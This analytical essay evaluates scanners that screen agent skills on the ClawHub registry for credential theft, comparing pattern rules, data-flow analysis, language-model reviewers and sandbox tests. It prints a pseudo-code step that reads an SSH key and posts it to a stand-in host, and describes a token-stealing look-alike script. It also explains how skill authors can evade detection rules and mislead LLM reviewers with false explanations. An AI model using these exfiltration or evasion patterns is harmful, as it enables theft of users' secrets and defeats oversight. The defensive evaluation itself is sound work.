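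The best outside scanner missed 41 of the 91 malicious tasks, and the two that relied only on rules missed about two thirds or more. A clean report from Cisco's static mode would lower the risk from 11.9 to 9.7 per cent, which hardly affects whether to trust a skill with cloud keys. Figures from *Demystifying Detectors Guarding Agent Skill Hubs* lead to similar risks after a clean report, 8.9 per cent for Cisco's static mode and 7.3 per cent for SkillSpector's. A clean report from skillscan-security would lower the risk to 3.9 per cent, but that scanner also flags half of all harmless skills.

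AgentTrap's own review looks much better, but Zhuang and colleagues wrote its instructions and also built 81 of the 91 malicious tasks. They took the other 10 from skills on ClawHub. They chose the tasks to cover 16 kinds of harm evenly, including altered output and wasted resources, so the detection rates don't measure credential theft alone. A scanner could do better against the attacks that are most common in registries.

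If malicious skills are rare, almost every skill with a clean report is harmless, mainly because almost every skill is harmless to begin with. If 0.16 per cent of skills are malicious, then at the detection rates in the table, a clean report from Cisco's static mode lowers the risk that a skill is malicious only from 1 in 625 to about 1 in 790.

Real attackers may evade detection more often than the test attacks did, because they can run a public scanner on their own skill before publishing it. In June 2026, the security firm Trail of Bits reported in *The sorry state of skill distribution* that it had got its own malicious test skills past several deployed scanners.

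Counts of known malicious skills are also a poor guide to what scanners miss. Liu and colleagues searched only among skills that matched a static pattern, so the 157 malicious skills they found include none that steal data in a way no pattern covers. Missing such skills doesn't lower a scanner's score in a test based on that collection.

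## Does it help to check whether the credential reaches the network?

Rules that report a network import or environment read on its own flag many legitimate programs, so some scanners require more evidence. Some rules report a problem only if the same file both reads the environment and uses the network. Data-flow analysis goes further and traces the credential to see whether it ends up in a request. This removes some false alarms, but a legitimate API client also sends its key in a request, so the finding doesn't show whether the key is going to the right place.

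### Rules that need both signals

Since at least March 2026, ClawHub has had a rule that reports a critical finding when a code file contains both `process.env` and network activity such as `fetch`, `http.request` or `axios`. CertiK, a security company with its own skill scanner, describes the rule from ClawHub's public source code in its post *Skill Scanning Is Not a Security Boundary*.

In JavaScript, the core of the GitHub script would look like this:

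```javascript
const token = process.env.GITHUB_TOKEN;
const r = await fetch(`https://api.github.com/repos/${repo}/issues`, {
  headers: { Authorization: `Bearer ${token}` },
});
```

The rule would report these lines as a critical finding but would not report the Python original, which does the same thing without containing any of those names.

As CertiK describes it, the rule also doesn't check whether the code sends the value it reads, so it flags a file that reads a harmless setting such as `MCP_HTTP_PORT` and makes a network request.

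The rule seems to check each file separately, so it would also miss skills that read all settings in one file and make all requests in another, as many do. CertiK also rewrote code so that it behaved the same but no longer matched, and used such rewrites in its test skills.

### Do the two signals go together in malicious skills?

Liu and colleagues argue that credential harvesting and external transmission can each be harmless, but that their co-occurrence signals intent. Their evidence is a count of the two patterns in 157 malicious skills:

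| | External transmission | No external transmission | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Credential harvesting | 58 | 43 | 101 |
| No credential harvesting | 21 | 35 | 56 |
| Total | 79 | 78 | 157 |

The odds ratio is 58 × 35 divided by 43 × 21, or about 2.2. External transmission appears in 57 per cent of the skills with credential harvesting and 38 per cent of the others, so it is about 1.5 times as likely in skills with harvesting. Liu and colleagues say it is 2.2 times as likely because they read the odds ratio as a ratio of probabilities. If the two patterns were unrelated, about 51 skills would be expected to contain both, which is not far below the actual 58.

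The statistical evidence is also weaker than Liu and colleagues claim. They report a p-value of 0.020 and say it remains significant after a Bonferroni correction, which lowers the threshold for significance when a study makes many comparisons. With the 91 pairs of patterns they mention, the threshold would be about 0.0005, far below 0.020.

The test also treats the 157 skills as independent, although one publisher made 85 of them from a single template. At least 83 of those 85 harvest credentials, which leaves at most 18 credential-harvesting skills from other publishers. So at least 40 of the 58 skills with both signals must come from that publisher.

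The pair is most common in the most elaborate skills. Liu and colleagues give percentages for three levels of sophistication, which work out to 1 of 25 basic skills, 48 of 122 intermediate ones and 9 of 10 advanced ones. Some rise is expected, because they define the levels partly by how many patterns a skill contains, and a skill with more patterns is more likely to contain any given pair. They nevertheless treat the rise as support for the levels. The low figure for basic skills matters more for a scanner, because a rule that requires the pair misses nearly all of the simplest attacks.

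The 43 skills with harvesting alone are a little puzzling, because Liu and colleagues say that they confirmed a skill with this pattern only if a test run showed a credential leaving the machine. Perhaps a downloaded program sent the credential in many of these cases.

The biggest problem is that the table contains no harmless skills, so it can show that the two signals occur together in malicious skills but not that the pair is rarer in harmless ones. Of the malicious skills, 122 contain at least one signal and 58 contain both, so a rule that requires both keeps 48 per cent of the detections. This improves precision only if fewer than 48 per cent of the harmless skills with at least one signal have both.

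Checking for a credential as well as network use probably helps, because plenty of harmless scripts use the network without a key. In the library of 163 research skills, paired rules produced critical findings for at most 11 skills, or 7 per cent, compared with 37 per cent of the malicious skills that Liu and colleagues labelled. If those figures held for a whole registry, the pair would be about five times as common in malicious skills as in others. That would make it useful for deciding what to read first, but if 0.16 per cent of skills are malicious, fewer than 1 in 100 matches would be malicious. The comparison is crude, since Liu and colleagues labelled their skills by hand and the library's findings came from an automatic scanner.

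### Following the token through the GitHub script

Data-flow analysis checks whether a particular value can reach a particular call. The analyzer needs a list of sources, such as reads of environment variables, and a list of sinks, such as functions that send data. It marks every value that comes from a source and every new value the program builds from a marked one.

| Line | Code | What the analyzer does |
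|---|---|---|
| 5 | `token = os.environ["GITHUB_TOKEN"]` | Recognises a source and marks `token` |
| 6 | `headers = {"Authorization": f"Bearer {token}"}` | Marks `headers`, because its text contains `token` |
| 9 | `requests.get(..., headers=headers)` | Links `headers` inside the function to the variable on line 6, recognises a sink and reports a flow |

The step from line 6 to line 9 is harder than it looks because `open_issues` doesn't receive `headers` as an argument. The analyzer has to account for Python functions using variables defined outside them. If `headers` were passed as an argument, as in `open_issues(repo, headers)`, the analyzer would match each argument in the call to a parameter in the definition, follow the marks through the function and carry any marked result back to the caller.

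The analyzer also needs a rule for marking the result of a call. Line 9 stores GitHub's reply in `r`, and line 14 prints the titles of the issues. If every result inherited the marks of every input, the analyzer would treat the reply as secret and report line 14 for printing a credential. *From Instructions to Exploits* avoids this mistake with rules under which the address of a request affects how far the analyzer trusts the reply, but the data sent with the request does not affect how the reply is marked.

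Data-flow analysis is more accurate than a paired rule for a program that reads `MCP_HTTP_PORT` and downloads a price list. The port goes to the function that starts the local server, and the download request contains nothing from the environment, so the analyzer reports no flow. Data-flow analysis also works when the address is in a variable or the call spans several lines, two cases where the text pattern E1 failed.

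An analyzer's false positives depend partly on whether it marks whole data structures or the individual values in them. Suppose a script copies the whole environment into a dictionary called `config` and sends only `config["AWS_REGION"]`. An analyzer that marks the whole dictionary will report a leak, even though the script sends only a region name. Tracking each entry separately avoids this false positive, but the analyzer then has to determine which entry the program uses, and the program may not choose the entry until it runs.

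### The same flow with a different destination

The analyzer would report the same path, from line 5 through line 6 to line 9, for the GitHub script's twin, which has `github-api.example` as its host. A more exact trace wouldn't help, because the two scripts handle the token identically until it leaves the machine.

To tell whether a credential is going where it belongs, a scanner has to extract the address from the network call and compare its full host name with the hosts expected for that credential. Searching the address for a familiar name isn't enough. `https://api.github.com.example.net/` belongs to whoever owns `example.net`, and in `https://example.net/api.github.com/` the familiar name is only part of the path.

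A script could send a token to the right host and still expose it, for example by uploading it to GitHub as the text of a public file. The scanner would therefore also need to check that the token is sent in the header the service uses for authentication. A server can also redirect the request to a different host. Python's `requests` then drops the `Authorization` header but keeps custom headers, which many services use for their keys.

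A credential flowing to an unknown host is a much more specific warning than "this skill reads a key and uses the network", and it gives the reviewer a host to look up. It still doesn't prove theft, because the host may be the employer's gateway.

### SCS: one graph for instructions and code

Ordinary data-flow analysis covers only code, while a skill's instructions can tell the agent to carry data from one step to the next. *From Instructions to Exploits* presents a scanner called SCS that tries to trace both. It divides SKILL.md into steps and has a language model translate each one into simple statements from a fixed list of operations. An instruction to read an SSH key and upload it becomes:

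```
v0 = read_file("~/.ssh/id_rsa")
http_post("https://example.com", v0)
```

Steps that only explain or describe something produce no statements. SCS rejects any statement that uses an unknown operation or an undefined variable and returns it to the model for correction. It also repairs some broken links, such as when the model repeats a file's name instead of using the variable that holds its contents.

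SCS also parses the skill's Python, JavaScript and shell scripts, and combines everything into one dependence graph, which shows which operations use the results of others. In the presentation skill with the malicious backup script, a path in the graph leads from the instruction to back up the finished file, through the script's argument, to the upload.

Each value in the graph has a trust level, a record of the operations that produced it, and a sensitivity level of PUBLIC, INTERNAL, SYSTEM, SENSITIVE or SECRET. When several values combine, the result takes the highest sensitivity and the lowest trust among them. SCS repeats this until no value changes, then applies fixed rules. If a value rated SENSITIVE or higher goes into the outgoing data of a network request, SCS reports possible exfiltration.

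In SCS's list of operations for instructions, an environment variable starts at INTERNAL, two levels below the threshold, so a flow from `GITHUB_TOKEN` would count only if SCS raised the level because of the variable's name. The paper explains such adjustments for file paths but not for variable names, so SCS, too, may well use a word list to decide what counts as a secret.

SCS recognises trusted hosts, but the only effect the paper mentions is that SCS treats their replies as more trustworthy. Surprisingly, no published rule cancels an exfiltration finding when the data goes to the service that issued the key. As described, SCS would treat the GitHub script and its twin alike. It flags both if it rates the token SENSITIVE and counts headers as outgoing data; otherwise, it misses a theft that uses the header.

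### How well SCS works

The paper compares SCS with seven other tools on 117 malicious and 117 harmless skills. Tools that need a language model ran with five models. The table shows five of the eight tools. Its counts are calculated from the published percentages and averaged across models for tools that ran with several.

| Tool | Malicious skills flagged | Harmless skills flagged | Precision |
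|---|---|---|---|
| SCS | 111 of 117 | 28 of 117 | 80% |
| A.I.G | 99 of 117 | 21 of 117 | 82% |
| Cisco's scanner with a language model | 105 of 117 | 62 of 117 | 63% |
| SkillFortify | 107 of 117 | 80 of 117 | 57% |
| SkillLeakBench | 55 of 117 | 19 of 117 | 74% |

SCS catches the largest number of malicious skills but still flags about a quarter of the harmless ones. It flagged 14 harmless skills when run with Claude Sonnet 4.6 and 34 with GPT-5.4, even though fixed rules produce most of its findings.

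SCS also has the highest average accuracy, but this is weaker support for data-flow analysis than it seems, because its lead over A.I.G, a Tencent scanner that relies on a language model's judgement, comes from one of the five models. With Sonnet 4.6, SCS classified 208 of the 234 skills correctly and A.I.G classified 207. The two tied with Qwen3, and A.I.G did slightly better with GPT-5.4 and DeepSeek-R1. With GPT-OSS-120B, however, SCS classified 198 correctly and A.I.G only 163. SCS therefore seems to work better with a weak model. It also used less than a quarter as many tokens as A.I.G.

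The harmless half of the test set, 117 skills, came from two earlier studies and from ClawHub's most-installed skills, and the researchers checked every skill by hand. Popular skills are a reasonable choice because many probably use real services and real keys. But the paper doesn't report how many of the 117 do, or what triggered the false positives, so legitimate API clients could account for most of the 28 wrongly flagged skills or hardly any.

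When the researchers ran SCS on 66,157 skills from ClawHub, it flagged 2,473, or 3.7 per cent. Reviewers confirmed 627 of these as malicious with the help of test runs. Even if all the unconfirmed skills were harmless, SCS flagged only 2.8 per cent of the registry's harmless skills, compared with 24 per cent in the test. This may be because many registry skills contain less code than popular ones, but the paper doesn't discuss the difference.

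Reviewers confirmed 627 of the selected skills, or about one in four, which would be a good rate for a registry scan. However, two accounts published 552 of the 627. Without those accounts, reviewers confirmed 75 of roughly 1,920 candidates, or about 4 per cent. The paper also doesn't break the 627 down by type of attack. If the two accounts mostly published skills with fake installation steps, as in the earlier ClawHub campaign, most of these detections have little to do with credentials reaching the network.

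The researchers also tested the translation of instructions on 400 steps from different skills. Depending on the model, 92.5 to 94.5 per cent of the translations were fully correct. The score for preserving links between operations was at least 99.5 per cent, but a step with no links counts as correct if the model adds none. Only 56 of the 400 steps came from passages with several operations. The test is therefore weaker evidence about long chains, where one wrong link can hide a theft.

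The paper also doesn't compare the full system with a version that traces only code. The researchers argue that removing an early stage would leave the later ones without input. But they could have run the code part of the graph without the instructions, which would have shown how much the joint graph adds.

### SkillFortify and its zero false positives

The information-flow check in SkillFortify, the tool in *Formal Analysis and Supply Chain Security for Agentic AI Skills*, detected no malicious skills beyond those found by text patterns. It fired 44 times on 270 malicious skills, always on a skill that the patterns had already flagged. The paper reports this as a negative result, although its introduction claims that combining the two finds attacks that patterns alone miss.

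The result is weak evidence about real data-flow analysis, because SkillFortify doesn't map how the program runs. Its check is closer to a paired rule that looks for base64 encoding together with an untrusted network destination. In one of the paper's examples, a skill copies the whole environment into a variable and posts it to an outside server as "telemetry". According to the paper, SkillFortify traces this flow from source to sink. But the code contains no encoding, and all 44 findings in the experiment were in the encoded-payload category.

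SkillFortify also offers a mathematical guarantee, but it covers only the operations the tool extracts from a skill. The tool assigns each skill an access level (NONE, READ, WRITE or ADMIN) for each of eight resources, including the network and the environment. A web address implies at least READ for the network, a request that posts data implies WRITE, and a reference to an environment variable implies READ for the environment. SkillFortify then compares these levels with the permissions the skill declares. If no level exceeds the declared permissions, the theorem guarantees that the extracted operations stay within them.

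The GitHub script needs READ for both the network and the environment. Its twin needs the same permissions, because the levels don't record which host receives the data. A skill that steals the token therefore passes the check if it declares both permissions. The check still correctly proves that the skill does no more than it declares, which is useful for enforcing permissions but doesn't show that the token is safe. If a skill declares no permissions, the check has nothing to compare its code against.

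SkillFortify had zero false positives on 270 generated harmless skills, which were designed to avoid unnecessary network access, process execution and exposure of environment variables. The categories include wrappers for web services, but the paper doesn't report how many harmless skills read a key and send it. The example it prints formats JSON files and only needs to read local files.

The SCS comparison is a much harder test. SkillFortify's recall was 91.5 per cent, close to the 92.6 per cent on its own benchmark. But it flagged 80 of the 117 harmless skills (68 per cent), compared with none of the 270 in its own benchmark. The two tests may have used different versions or thresholds, and the SCS researchers had a competing tool to promote. Even so, such a large gap suggests that the absence of false positives on SkillFortify's own benchmark came mainly from using artificial skills. The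 SkillFortify paper's confidence interval, which puts the false-positive rate below 1.4 per cent, applies only to skills from the same generator.

### Where the trace breaks off

Programs often choose the destination while they are running. A small change would let the GitHub script work with a company's own GitHub server:

```python
base = os.environ.get("GITHUB_API_URL", "https://api.github.com")
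r = requests.get(f"{base}/repos/{repo}/issues", headers=headers)
```

Static analysis can find the default address, but not the value the variable will have on the user's machine. If the scanner uses the default, it will miss a skill whose instructions tell the agent to set `GITHUB_API_URL` to an attacker's server. If it treats every configurable address as unknown, it will flag many well-written clients. SCS's list of operations includes setting environment variables, so it could in principle connect such an instruction to the script, but the paper gives no example. SkillFortify's guarantee explicitly excludes addresses a program reads from a file and commands it assembles while running.

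Code that a program generates or downloads causes a similar problem, because the sink may not exist when the scanner runs. SCS is also limited by its lists, which cover 191 Python functions, 91 JavaScript functions and 59 shell commands. According to the paper, SCS can miss calls to other libraries. It may also miss a secret that a user keeps in a file with an uninformative name.

Skills that combine several languages are especially hard to analyze. Cisco's optional behavioural analyzer covers only Python, so it can't trace a theft written in JavaScript. A Python script can also start a JavaScript program that inherits its environment and reads the token there. If the script passes nothing to that program directly, the Python file contains no flow to report. SCS parses both languages, but would need a separate trace that starts in the JavaScript file. If the Python script instead writes the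 token to a temporary file that the JavaScript program reads, the analyzer has to detect that both use the same file, which may be impossible if the script generates the filename at runtime.

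## Can stated purpose, a language model or a test run tell use from theft?

A data-flow trace can show which key leaves the machine and often which host receives it, but not whether the user would approve. The skill's own description may partly answer that. A scanner can compare the description with the code, or use a language model to do so. It can also run the skill with fake keys and record where they go.

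### Comparing the code with the stated purpose

A declared-capability check compares what the author says a skill needs with what the code uses. The GitHub script reads `GITHUB_TOKEN` and contacts api.github.com. If the author lists that variable in the metadata and describes the skill as summarising GitHub issues, the code matches the declaration. The same code would not match the description of a skill that converts recipes to metric units, although a data-flow analyzer would report the same path in both skills.

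Hosts are harder to compare than variables because the base skill format has no field for them. The scanner has to infer from the description which services the skill should contact, and a description such as "tracks your portfolio" could fit many services.

OpenClaw's *Security Audits*, the guide to ClawHub's reviews, says that reviews mainly check coherence, meaning whether a skill's name, summary, metadata, requested access and content match what a user would reasonably expect. Powerful access is acceptable if it is "expected, disclosed, and proportionate". ClawHub gives each skill two ratings. The risk level describes how much power the skill has when it works as intended, and the audit status indicates how the user should respond. A publishing tool can have a Medium risk level and the status Review without suspicion of malice. This suits benign true positives because the audit can report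 a powerful key without calling its use theft.

### Three reviews from ClawHub

A language model writes the reviews that ClawHub publishes. One of them, *ClawScan security* (2026), covers a skill that lists the user's installed skills and reports them to a service called Clawned. The skill requires one credential, `CLAWNED_API_KEY`, which the review accepts as proportionate for a program that has to log in to a remote dashboard. Pattern rules had flagged the skill for credentials and exfiltration, and the review marks both findings as "expected". The code reads OpenClaw's configuration file only to find more skill folders, and it contacts a remote server to report the installed skills.

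The verdict was benign with high confidence, although according to the review, one command uploads up to 30 files from a folder the user chooses. The command skips `.env` files but takes other configuration files, which may well contain secrets. "Benign" here means that the skill's behavior matches its stated purpose, and the user still has to decide whether to trust Clawned with the files.

Another review covers Openclaw Egress, a skill that searches other skills for outgoing network calls. A text rule would flag its code, which is full of patterns for network libraries and web addresses. ClawHub marked these patterns as expected in a traffic scanner but still rated the skill suspicious, because the script could also write an allowlist and apparently rename or block other skills. The documentation described a free version that only raises alerts. ClawHub inferred some of these abilities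 from names in the code, such as `QUARANTINE_PREFIX`. They could be left over from a paid version, but a user would want to know about them either way.

ClawHub's *Agent Security Skill Scanner Gitee* reviews a scanner that can send code to a language model for analysis. The skill's documentation tells users to set `LLM_API_KEY`, but its metadata lists no environment variables. The review says the key is expected for the advertised feature and rates the missing declaration Low. An instruction to start a background script that isn't in the package gets a higher rating, Medium. A rule that matches names would mainly have flagged the key, which the review rated the less serious problem.

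### Poor metadata and plausible metadata

Honest authors often leave metadata incomplete. A key may be optional, or the author may have added a feature and forgotten to update the frontmatter. In *After the Party*, Xiong and Zhang (2026) searched 64,324 ClawHub skills for twelve kinds of powerful access, including network and credential access. For each kind, their detector looked first for a declaration in the frontmatter and then for patterns in the text. Only 450 of its 153,986 matches (0.3 per cent) came from declarations.

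The text patterns are rough because they can count a web address as network access, and the detector may not recognise every field that authors use. Even so, undeclared access is clearly normal, and a scanner that treated every missing declaration as deception would flag most of the registry.

Missing files cause a similar problem. ClawHub rated a skill called Devin Floyd suspicious because its documentation included a step to run `scan.py`, which wasn't in the package. The author may have forgotten to upload the file. But attackers in the February ClawHub campaign also used fake installation steps to send users elsewhere for a program, so the warning was reasonable, although it is weak evidence of the author's intent.

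A thief can easily avoid these mistakes by declaring `GITHUB_TOKEN` in the malicious version of the GitHub script, describing the skill as an issue summariser and explaining that it reaches GitHub through a gateway at `github-api.example`. The description, metadata and code would then agree, so the skill would pass a declared-capability check and get past a reader who didn't ask who owns the gateway.

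Liu and colleagues provide a rough measure of this weakness. They compared the documentation of their 157 malicious skills with what the skills did when run, and in 115 of them found behaviour that nobody could infer from the documentation. The other 42, or 27 per cent, had no hidden behaviour by this definition, so even a careful comparison would not have exposed them. There is no matching count for harmless skills, so the comparison's false-positive rate is unknown.

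### How a language model receives the findings

A language model can judge whether a portfolio tracker should contact a currency exchange even if no metadata field mentions one. Systems in use differ in what they show the model and how much power they give it.

VirusTotal (2026) added support for OpenClaw skills to Code Insight, its language-model analysis. The model, Gemini 3 Flash, starts with SKILL.md and then reads the scripts and other files that SKILL.md refers to. Its task is to summarise what the skill does, such as whether it reads sensitive data or uses the network, rather than what it claims to do. Code Insight therefore starts from the package itself rather than another scanner's findings.

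ClawHub at first used this analysis to approve or block skills. The Hacker News reported in February 2026 that ClawHub computed a fingerprint of each skill, looked it up in VirusTotal's database and sent unknown skills to Code Insight. OpenClaw automatically approved skills judged benign, added a warning to suspicious ones and blocked malicious ones. It told publishers to expect some false positives.

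By the end of May, VirusTotal's result was only one input to ClawScan, ClawHub's own review. *ClawHub Security Signals* (Koc, Rivera and colleagues, 2026) describes how ClawScan gathers the results of VirusTotal, ClawHub's static rules and SkillSpector, adds the skill's metadata and origin, and has a language model give one verdict. An earlier version of *Security Audits* says that static findings are internal context for this review and cannot block an installation by themselves. The later version lists SkillSpector and A.I.G as the outside sources.

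The model often has to resolve conflicting scanner results. pkg.go.dev, a site that documents software packages, reproduces a sample ClawScan report on a skill that summarises CSV files. One scanner found nothing and rated the skill safe, but SkillSpector's recommendation was CAUTION, partly because of an E2 finding. Koc and colleagues found that such conflicts are the norm. Among 67,453 skills, 81.9 per cent of those flagged by any scanner were flagged by only one.

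ClawScan rated 25,504 of these skills suspicious and 206 malicious, so more than a third of the registry still carried a warning after the language model had considered the context. The number of correct warnings is unknown because the dataset's labels are ClawScan's own verdicts. According to the package documentation, the paper found that several scanners with a judge work better than one scanner, but labels that come from the judge can't establish that. Most of the paper's authors work on the tools it covers, at the OpenClaw Foundation and NVIDIA.

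In a small independent check by Xiong and Zhang, two people with software security experience labelled 180 ClawHub skills without seeing the scanners' results. The study then compared their labels with ClawHub's language-model, static and VirusTotal results. Recall ranged from 21.67 to 61.06 per cent, so the language model missed at least 39 per cent of the skills that the reviewers would have flagged. The reviewers flagged any definite concern that deserved a human look, including privacy problems, so the test was broader than malware detection. The study covers only 276 eligible skills, whose files had not changed since March.

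Cisco uses a language model more narrowly. Its *Frequently Asked Questions* describes an optional last step, the meta-analyzer, in which a language model reviews the findings of all the other analyzers and removes likely false positives. It could remove the misread `urllib` import, for example. But it cannot find a theft that every other analyzer missed, and it may remove the only finding that describes a real theft.

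Cisco also offers a consensus mode, which runs the language-model analyzer several times and keeps the findings that appear in most runs. This reduces random errors, but it doesn't help when something in the skill consistently misleads the model. If a false finding has a 30 per cent chance of appearing in each of three independent runs, it has about a 22 per cent chance of appearing in at least two. If its chance in each run is 90 per cent, its chance of appearing in at least two is about 97 per cent.

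### SkillSieve's four questions and its jury

Hou and Yang (2026), in *SkillSieve*, measure what happens when language models sort through static findings. Their scanner begins with text patterns, syntax trees and metadata, with a threshold low enough to let through as few malicious skills as possible. If a skill scores above the threshold, a language model receives the full skill and its static findings and answers four separate questions:

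- Does the skill do what its description says? (weight 0.35)
- Does it need the files, variables, programs and network access it uses? (0.25)
- Does it hide anything from the user or try to get around safety measures? (0.25)
- Do the scripts and commands match SKILL.md? (0.15)

Each answer is a score from 0 to 1. If the weighted sum is at least 0.4, the skill goes to a jury of three models from different companies. If the models disagree, each receives the others' evidence and votes again. If two models still classify the skill as safe and one as malicious, it stays blocked until a person reviews it.

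Hou and Yang tested this on 55 malicious and 335 harmless skills, nearly all from ClawHub:

| Stage | Malicious skills still flagged | Harmless skills still flagged | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| Static rules | 55 | 106 | 34% |
| After the four questions | 55 | 28 | 66% |
| After the jury | 52 | 5 | 91% |

The four questions cleared 78 of the 106 harmless skills and no malicious ones. The jury cleared another 23 harmless skills, but also 3 malicious ones.

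The first stage's perfect recall is less impressive than it looks because Hou and Yang chose its threshold of 0.3 after seeing that the lowest score of any malicious skill in this test was 0.35. They also report that many skills in the test share an author. When they tested a separate learned classifier on skills by authors absent from its training data, its F1 score (a combined measure of precision and recall) fell from 0.918 to 0.671. The full system might lose some accuracy on new authors too.

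About a third of the 28 harmless skills that remained after the four questions handled crypto wallets or decentralised finance. They use private keys and call exchanges, so the model scored them as slightly suspicious on one question after another. Because the scores are added in a weighted sum, a wallet skill that scores 0.4 on every question reaches the jury, even though no answer is alarming. No single question can send a skill to the jury on its own, since the largest weight is 0.35.

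Adding up the scores also favours a well-documented skill that steals. If the description matches the behaviour and nothing looks hidden, two questions score 0, and the other two must both score 1 for the total to reach 0.4. Hou and Yang suggest replacing the sum with a rule that forwards a skill only if at least one question gives a strong signal. That would probably clear more wallet skills and catch more cases with one glaring problem, but they haven't tested it.

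In a second test, Hou and Yang scanned 52 packages for Feishu, ByteDance's office communication platform. The static rules flagged 14, and the four questions cleared 13. The remaining package stored an app secret in an unencrypted file, which is a weakness but not theft. Most of the false alarms came from timestamps, long web addresses and a warning about prompt injection, not from network imports or environment reads. The result shows that a model can recognise misreadings in unfamiliar material, but it is weaker evidence of how a model handles honest API clients.

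### A rule match as supporting evidence

*The Devil Wears Markdown* tests a system that never treats a rule match as sufficient proof. Its static stage keeps each match with its severity and location, and passes it to a group of language-model agents. They compare it with the skill's purpose and with evidence from a test run, and have to cite a file or a log entry for their verdict. The paper gave the same agents different evidence about the same 80 malicious and 60 harmless skills:

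| Evidence | Malicious skills flagged | Harmless skills flagged |
|---|---|---|
| The skill's files only | 54 | 21 |
| Files and static findings | 28 | 3 |
| Files and a test run | 63 | 5 |
| Files, static findings and a test run | 68 | 5 |

Giving the agents static findings removed 18 of the 21 false positives, but the agents then missed 26 more malicious skills. The paper doesn't establish the cause. Median review time fell from 320 to 95 seconds, so the agents may have focused on the flagged lines and neglected the rest. The static rules were also written for general malware, not agent skills, and would have flagged little in an attack written in prose. A scanner that gives its model a short list of weak findings could lead it to treat the rest of a skill as safe when it isn't.

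When a test run was included, adding the static findings helped the system catch five more malicious skills without flagging any additional harmless ones. The value of a static finding therefore seems to depend on what other evidence the model has.

In `research-lookup`, one of the five false positives, the model identified the relevant code but misinterpreted it. The code reads `OPENROUTER_API_KEY` and sends it to an OpenRouter address in the authentication header. The variable name, host and header are all consistent with ordinary authentication, but the model labelled this data exfiltration with 90 per cent confidence. It also described the installation command as benign in one finding and as remote code execution in another. The final verdict was malware, with a score of 92 out of 100.

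A weak model can add false positives. One of the paper's tests added a small language model, Qwen3:8B, to Cisco's scanner. Without the model, the scanner raised at least one alert for 33 of the 60 harmless skills. With it, 40 failed the stricter `is_safe` test. Since a skill without alerts cannot fail `is_safe`, the model seems to have caused at least seven of these failures. The test didn't use Cisco's meta-analyzer, which filters out false positives, so it doesn't measure how well that filter works.

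### The author writes part of the evidence

Language models are useful here because they can read explanations, but this is also their main weakness, since the skill's author wrote the description, comments, variable names and documentation. ClawScan also considers context that the publisher provides. A thief can use any of these to give the same reason for needing a key that an honest author would give.

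A scanner can search for instructions aimed at the reviewing model, but it can't search for an ordinary false claim, such as that a server belongs to the company's analytics provider. The model can check whether the claim fits the code, but whether it is true depends on facts outside the package.

VirusTotal's instruction to describe what the skill does helps somewhat, because it makes the model rely less on the author's claims. The model still relies on them partly, because it has to decide whether a transfer is a leak or an upload the user wanted, and the skill's purpose usually comes from its documentation.

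The model may also rate a skill benign because nothing in it looks wrong. ClawHub used a language model to review Moltcops, a local security scanner, and rated it benign with medium confidence, while acknowledging that it could not fully verify how the bundled script behaves. It advised users to open the script and search for `requests`, `urllib`, `socket` and similar names. Users therefore had to check for network imports themselves, though many would assume the benign rating had already settled the question.

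### Running the skill with fake keys

A test run records what a program does, so it doesn't rely on the author's explanations. Liu and colleagues ran 4,287 skills that had matched a static pattern, each in a container, a closed-off environment with its own files and network connection. The containers held honeypot credentials, fake API and SSH keys used to see whether a skill would send them out. Monitoring tools recorded network traffic, file changes and programs' requests to the operating system.

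A program may steal a key only when the user takes a specific action, so Liu and colleagues started the skills in several ways. They used the documented entry points and had GPT-5.2 write three sets of inputs from each skill's description, one typical, one unusual and one hostile. Each skill ran three to five times with different inputs and a 60-second time limit.

A skill went to human review if it sent a fake credential to an outside address, showed other unexplained network activity, ran hidden code or gained higher privileges. Two researchers then compared its logs and code with its documentation. These triggers cover much more than leaked keys, which partly explains why most of the flagged skills were not confirmed cases.

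A leaked honeypot credential is much stronger evidence than a line of code that could leak one, because the transfer has happened and the log records the recipient. The reviewers, for example, disagreed about nine skills until they examined further evidence, such as network captures of a credential being sent.

A legitimate GitHub script run with a fake `GITHUB_TOKEN` will also send it to GitHub, so a better test adds fake keys that the skill has no reason to use, such as a cloud key. If the skill sends the cloud key anywhere, the cause is probably theft, a serious bug or an error report that includes too much data.

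Testers also have to find the key in the traffic. Most web services use encrypted connections, so a plain recording shows the host but not the contents. Testers usually route the traffic through a proxy that can decrypt it. If the program encodes or splits the key before sending it, a search for the original text would still find nothing.

A quiet run is weak evidence that a skill is safe, because theft may depend on a condition that the test didn't meet. Using fake keys can create this problem. GitHub rejects the fake token, and line 10 of the GitHub script, `r.raise_for_status()`, then stops the program, so the test would never reach any theft code that came after a successful request. Conditional triggers, such as a certain date, made up 18.4 per cent of the undocumented behaviours that Liu and colleagues recorded in the malicious skills they studied, and that figure covers only the triggers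 they found. The number of quiet skills that were dormant malware is disputed.

Suppose, for illustration, that half of all malicious skills leak an unrelated fake key during a test, and that one harmless skill in 1,000 does so by accident. If 11.9 per cent of skills are malicious, as in Koi's first audit, a leak raises the probability that a skill is malicious to 98.5 per cent, but a run without a leak lowers it only to 6.3 per cent. If 0.16 per cent are malicious, a leak still raises the probability to about 44 per cent.

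*The Devil Wears Markdown* uses a sandbox in which an agent carries out the skill's instructions as well as its scripts. This can expose theft directed by written instructions rather than code, which a test that only runs scripts would miss. The agent, Claude Opus 4.8, was told to skip dangerous actions and record them, so an upload it refused to make could count as evidence of malice even though no data left the machine.

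This makes the test safer but less independent. Some of the "test run" evidence is one language model's reading of the skill, passed to another. The agents that gave the verdict used Qwen models, so part of the improvement in the table may come from adding Claude's judgement rather than from observing behaviour. The paper has no comparison that separates the two effects. Each skill also ran only once, and a second run could have taken a different path.

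### Costs and errors compared

The methods differ more in the errors they add than in the errors they remove:

| Evidence | Main cost | Errors it removes | Errors it adds |
|---|---|---|---|
| Stated purpose | Almost none once the scanner has parsed the files | Warnings about declared keys and expected services | Flags honest skills with poor metadata; passes thieves with good metadata |
| Language-model review | A few cents per skill | Misreadings and many benign true positives | Mistakes ordinary logins for theft; believes false explanations |
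| Test run with fake keys | Minutes of computing per skill, and people to read the logs | Doubt about whether suspicious code really sends a key | Clears theft that the test didn't trigger; flags unusual but harmless tools |

Language-model review costs less if static rules filter the skills first. Hou and Yang's static stage scanned 49,592 ClawHub skills in 31 minutes on a $440 computer and passed 6,871 of them to language models. They estimate that the language-model calls cost about 4 cents for each of those skills, or $297 for the whole registry, compared with $496 if one model read every skill.

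Test runs mainly take up reviewers' time. Liu and colleagues' whole pipeline took roughly 72 hours on a 64-core server to process 98,380 skills, which is feasible for a registry. But two researchers each had to review 762 skills. Assuming ten minutes per skill, which is probably low for reading logs and code, the reviews took 254 hours in total.

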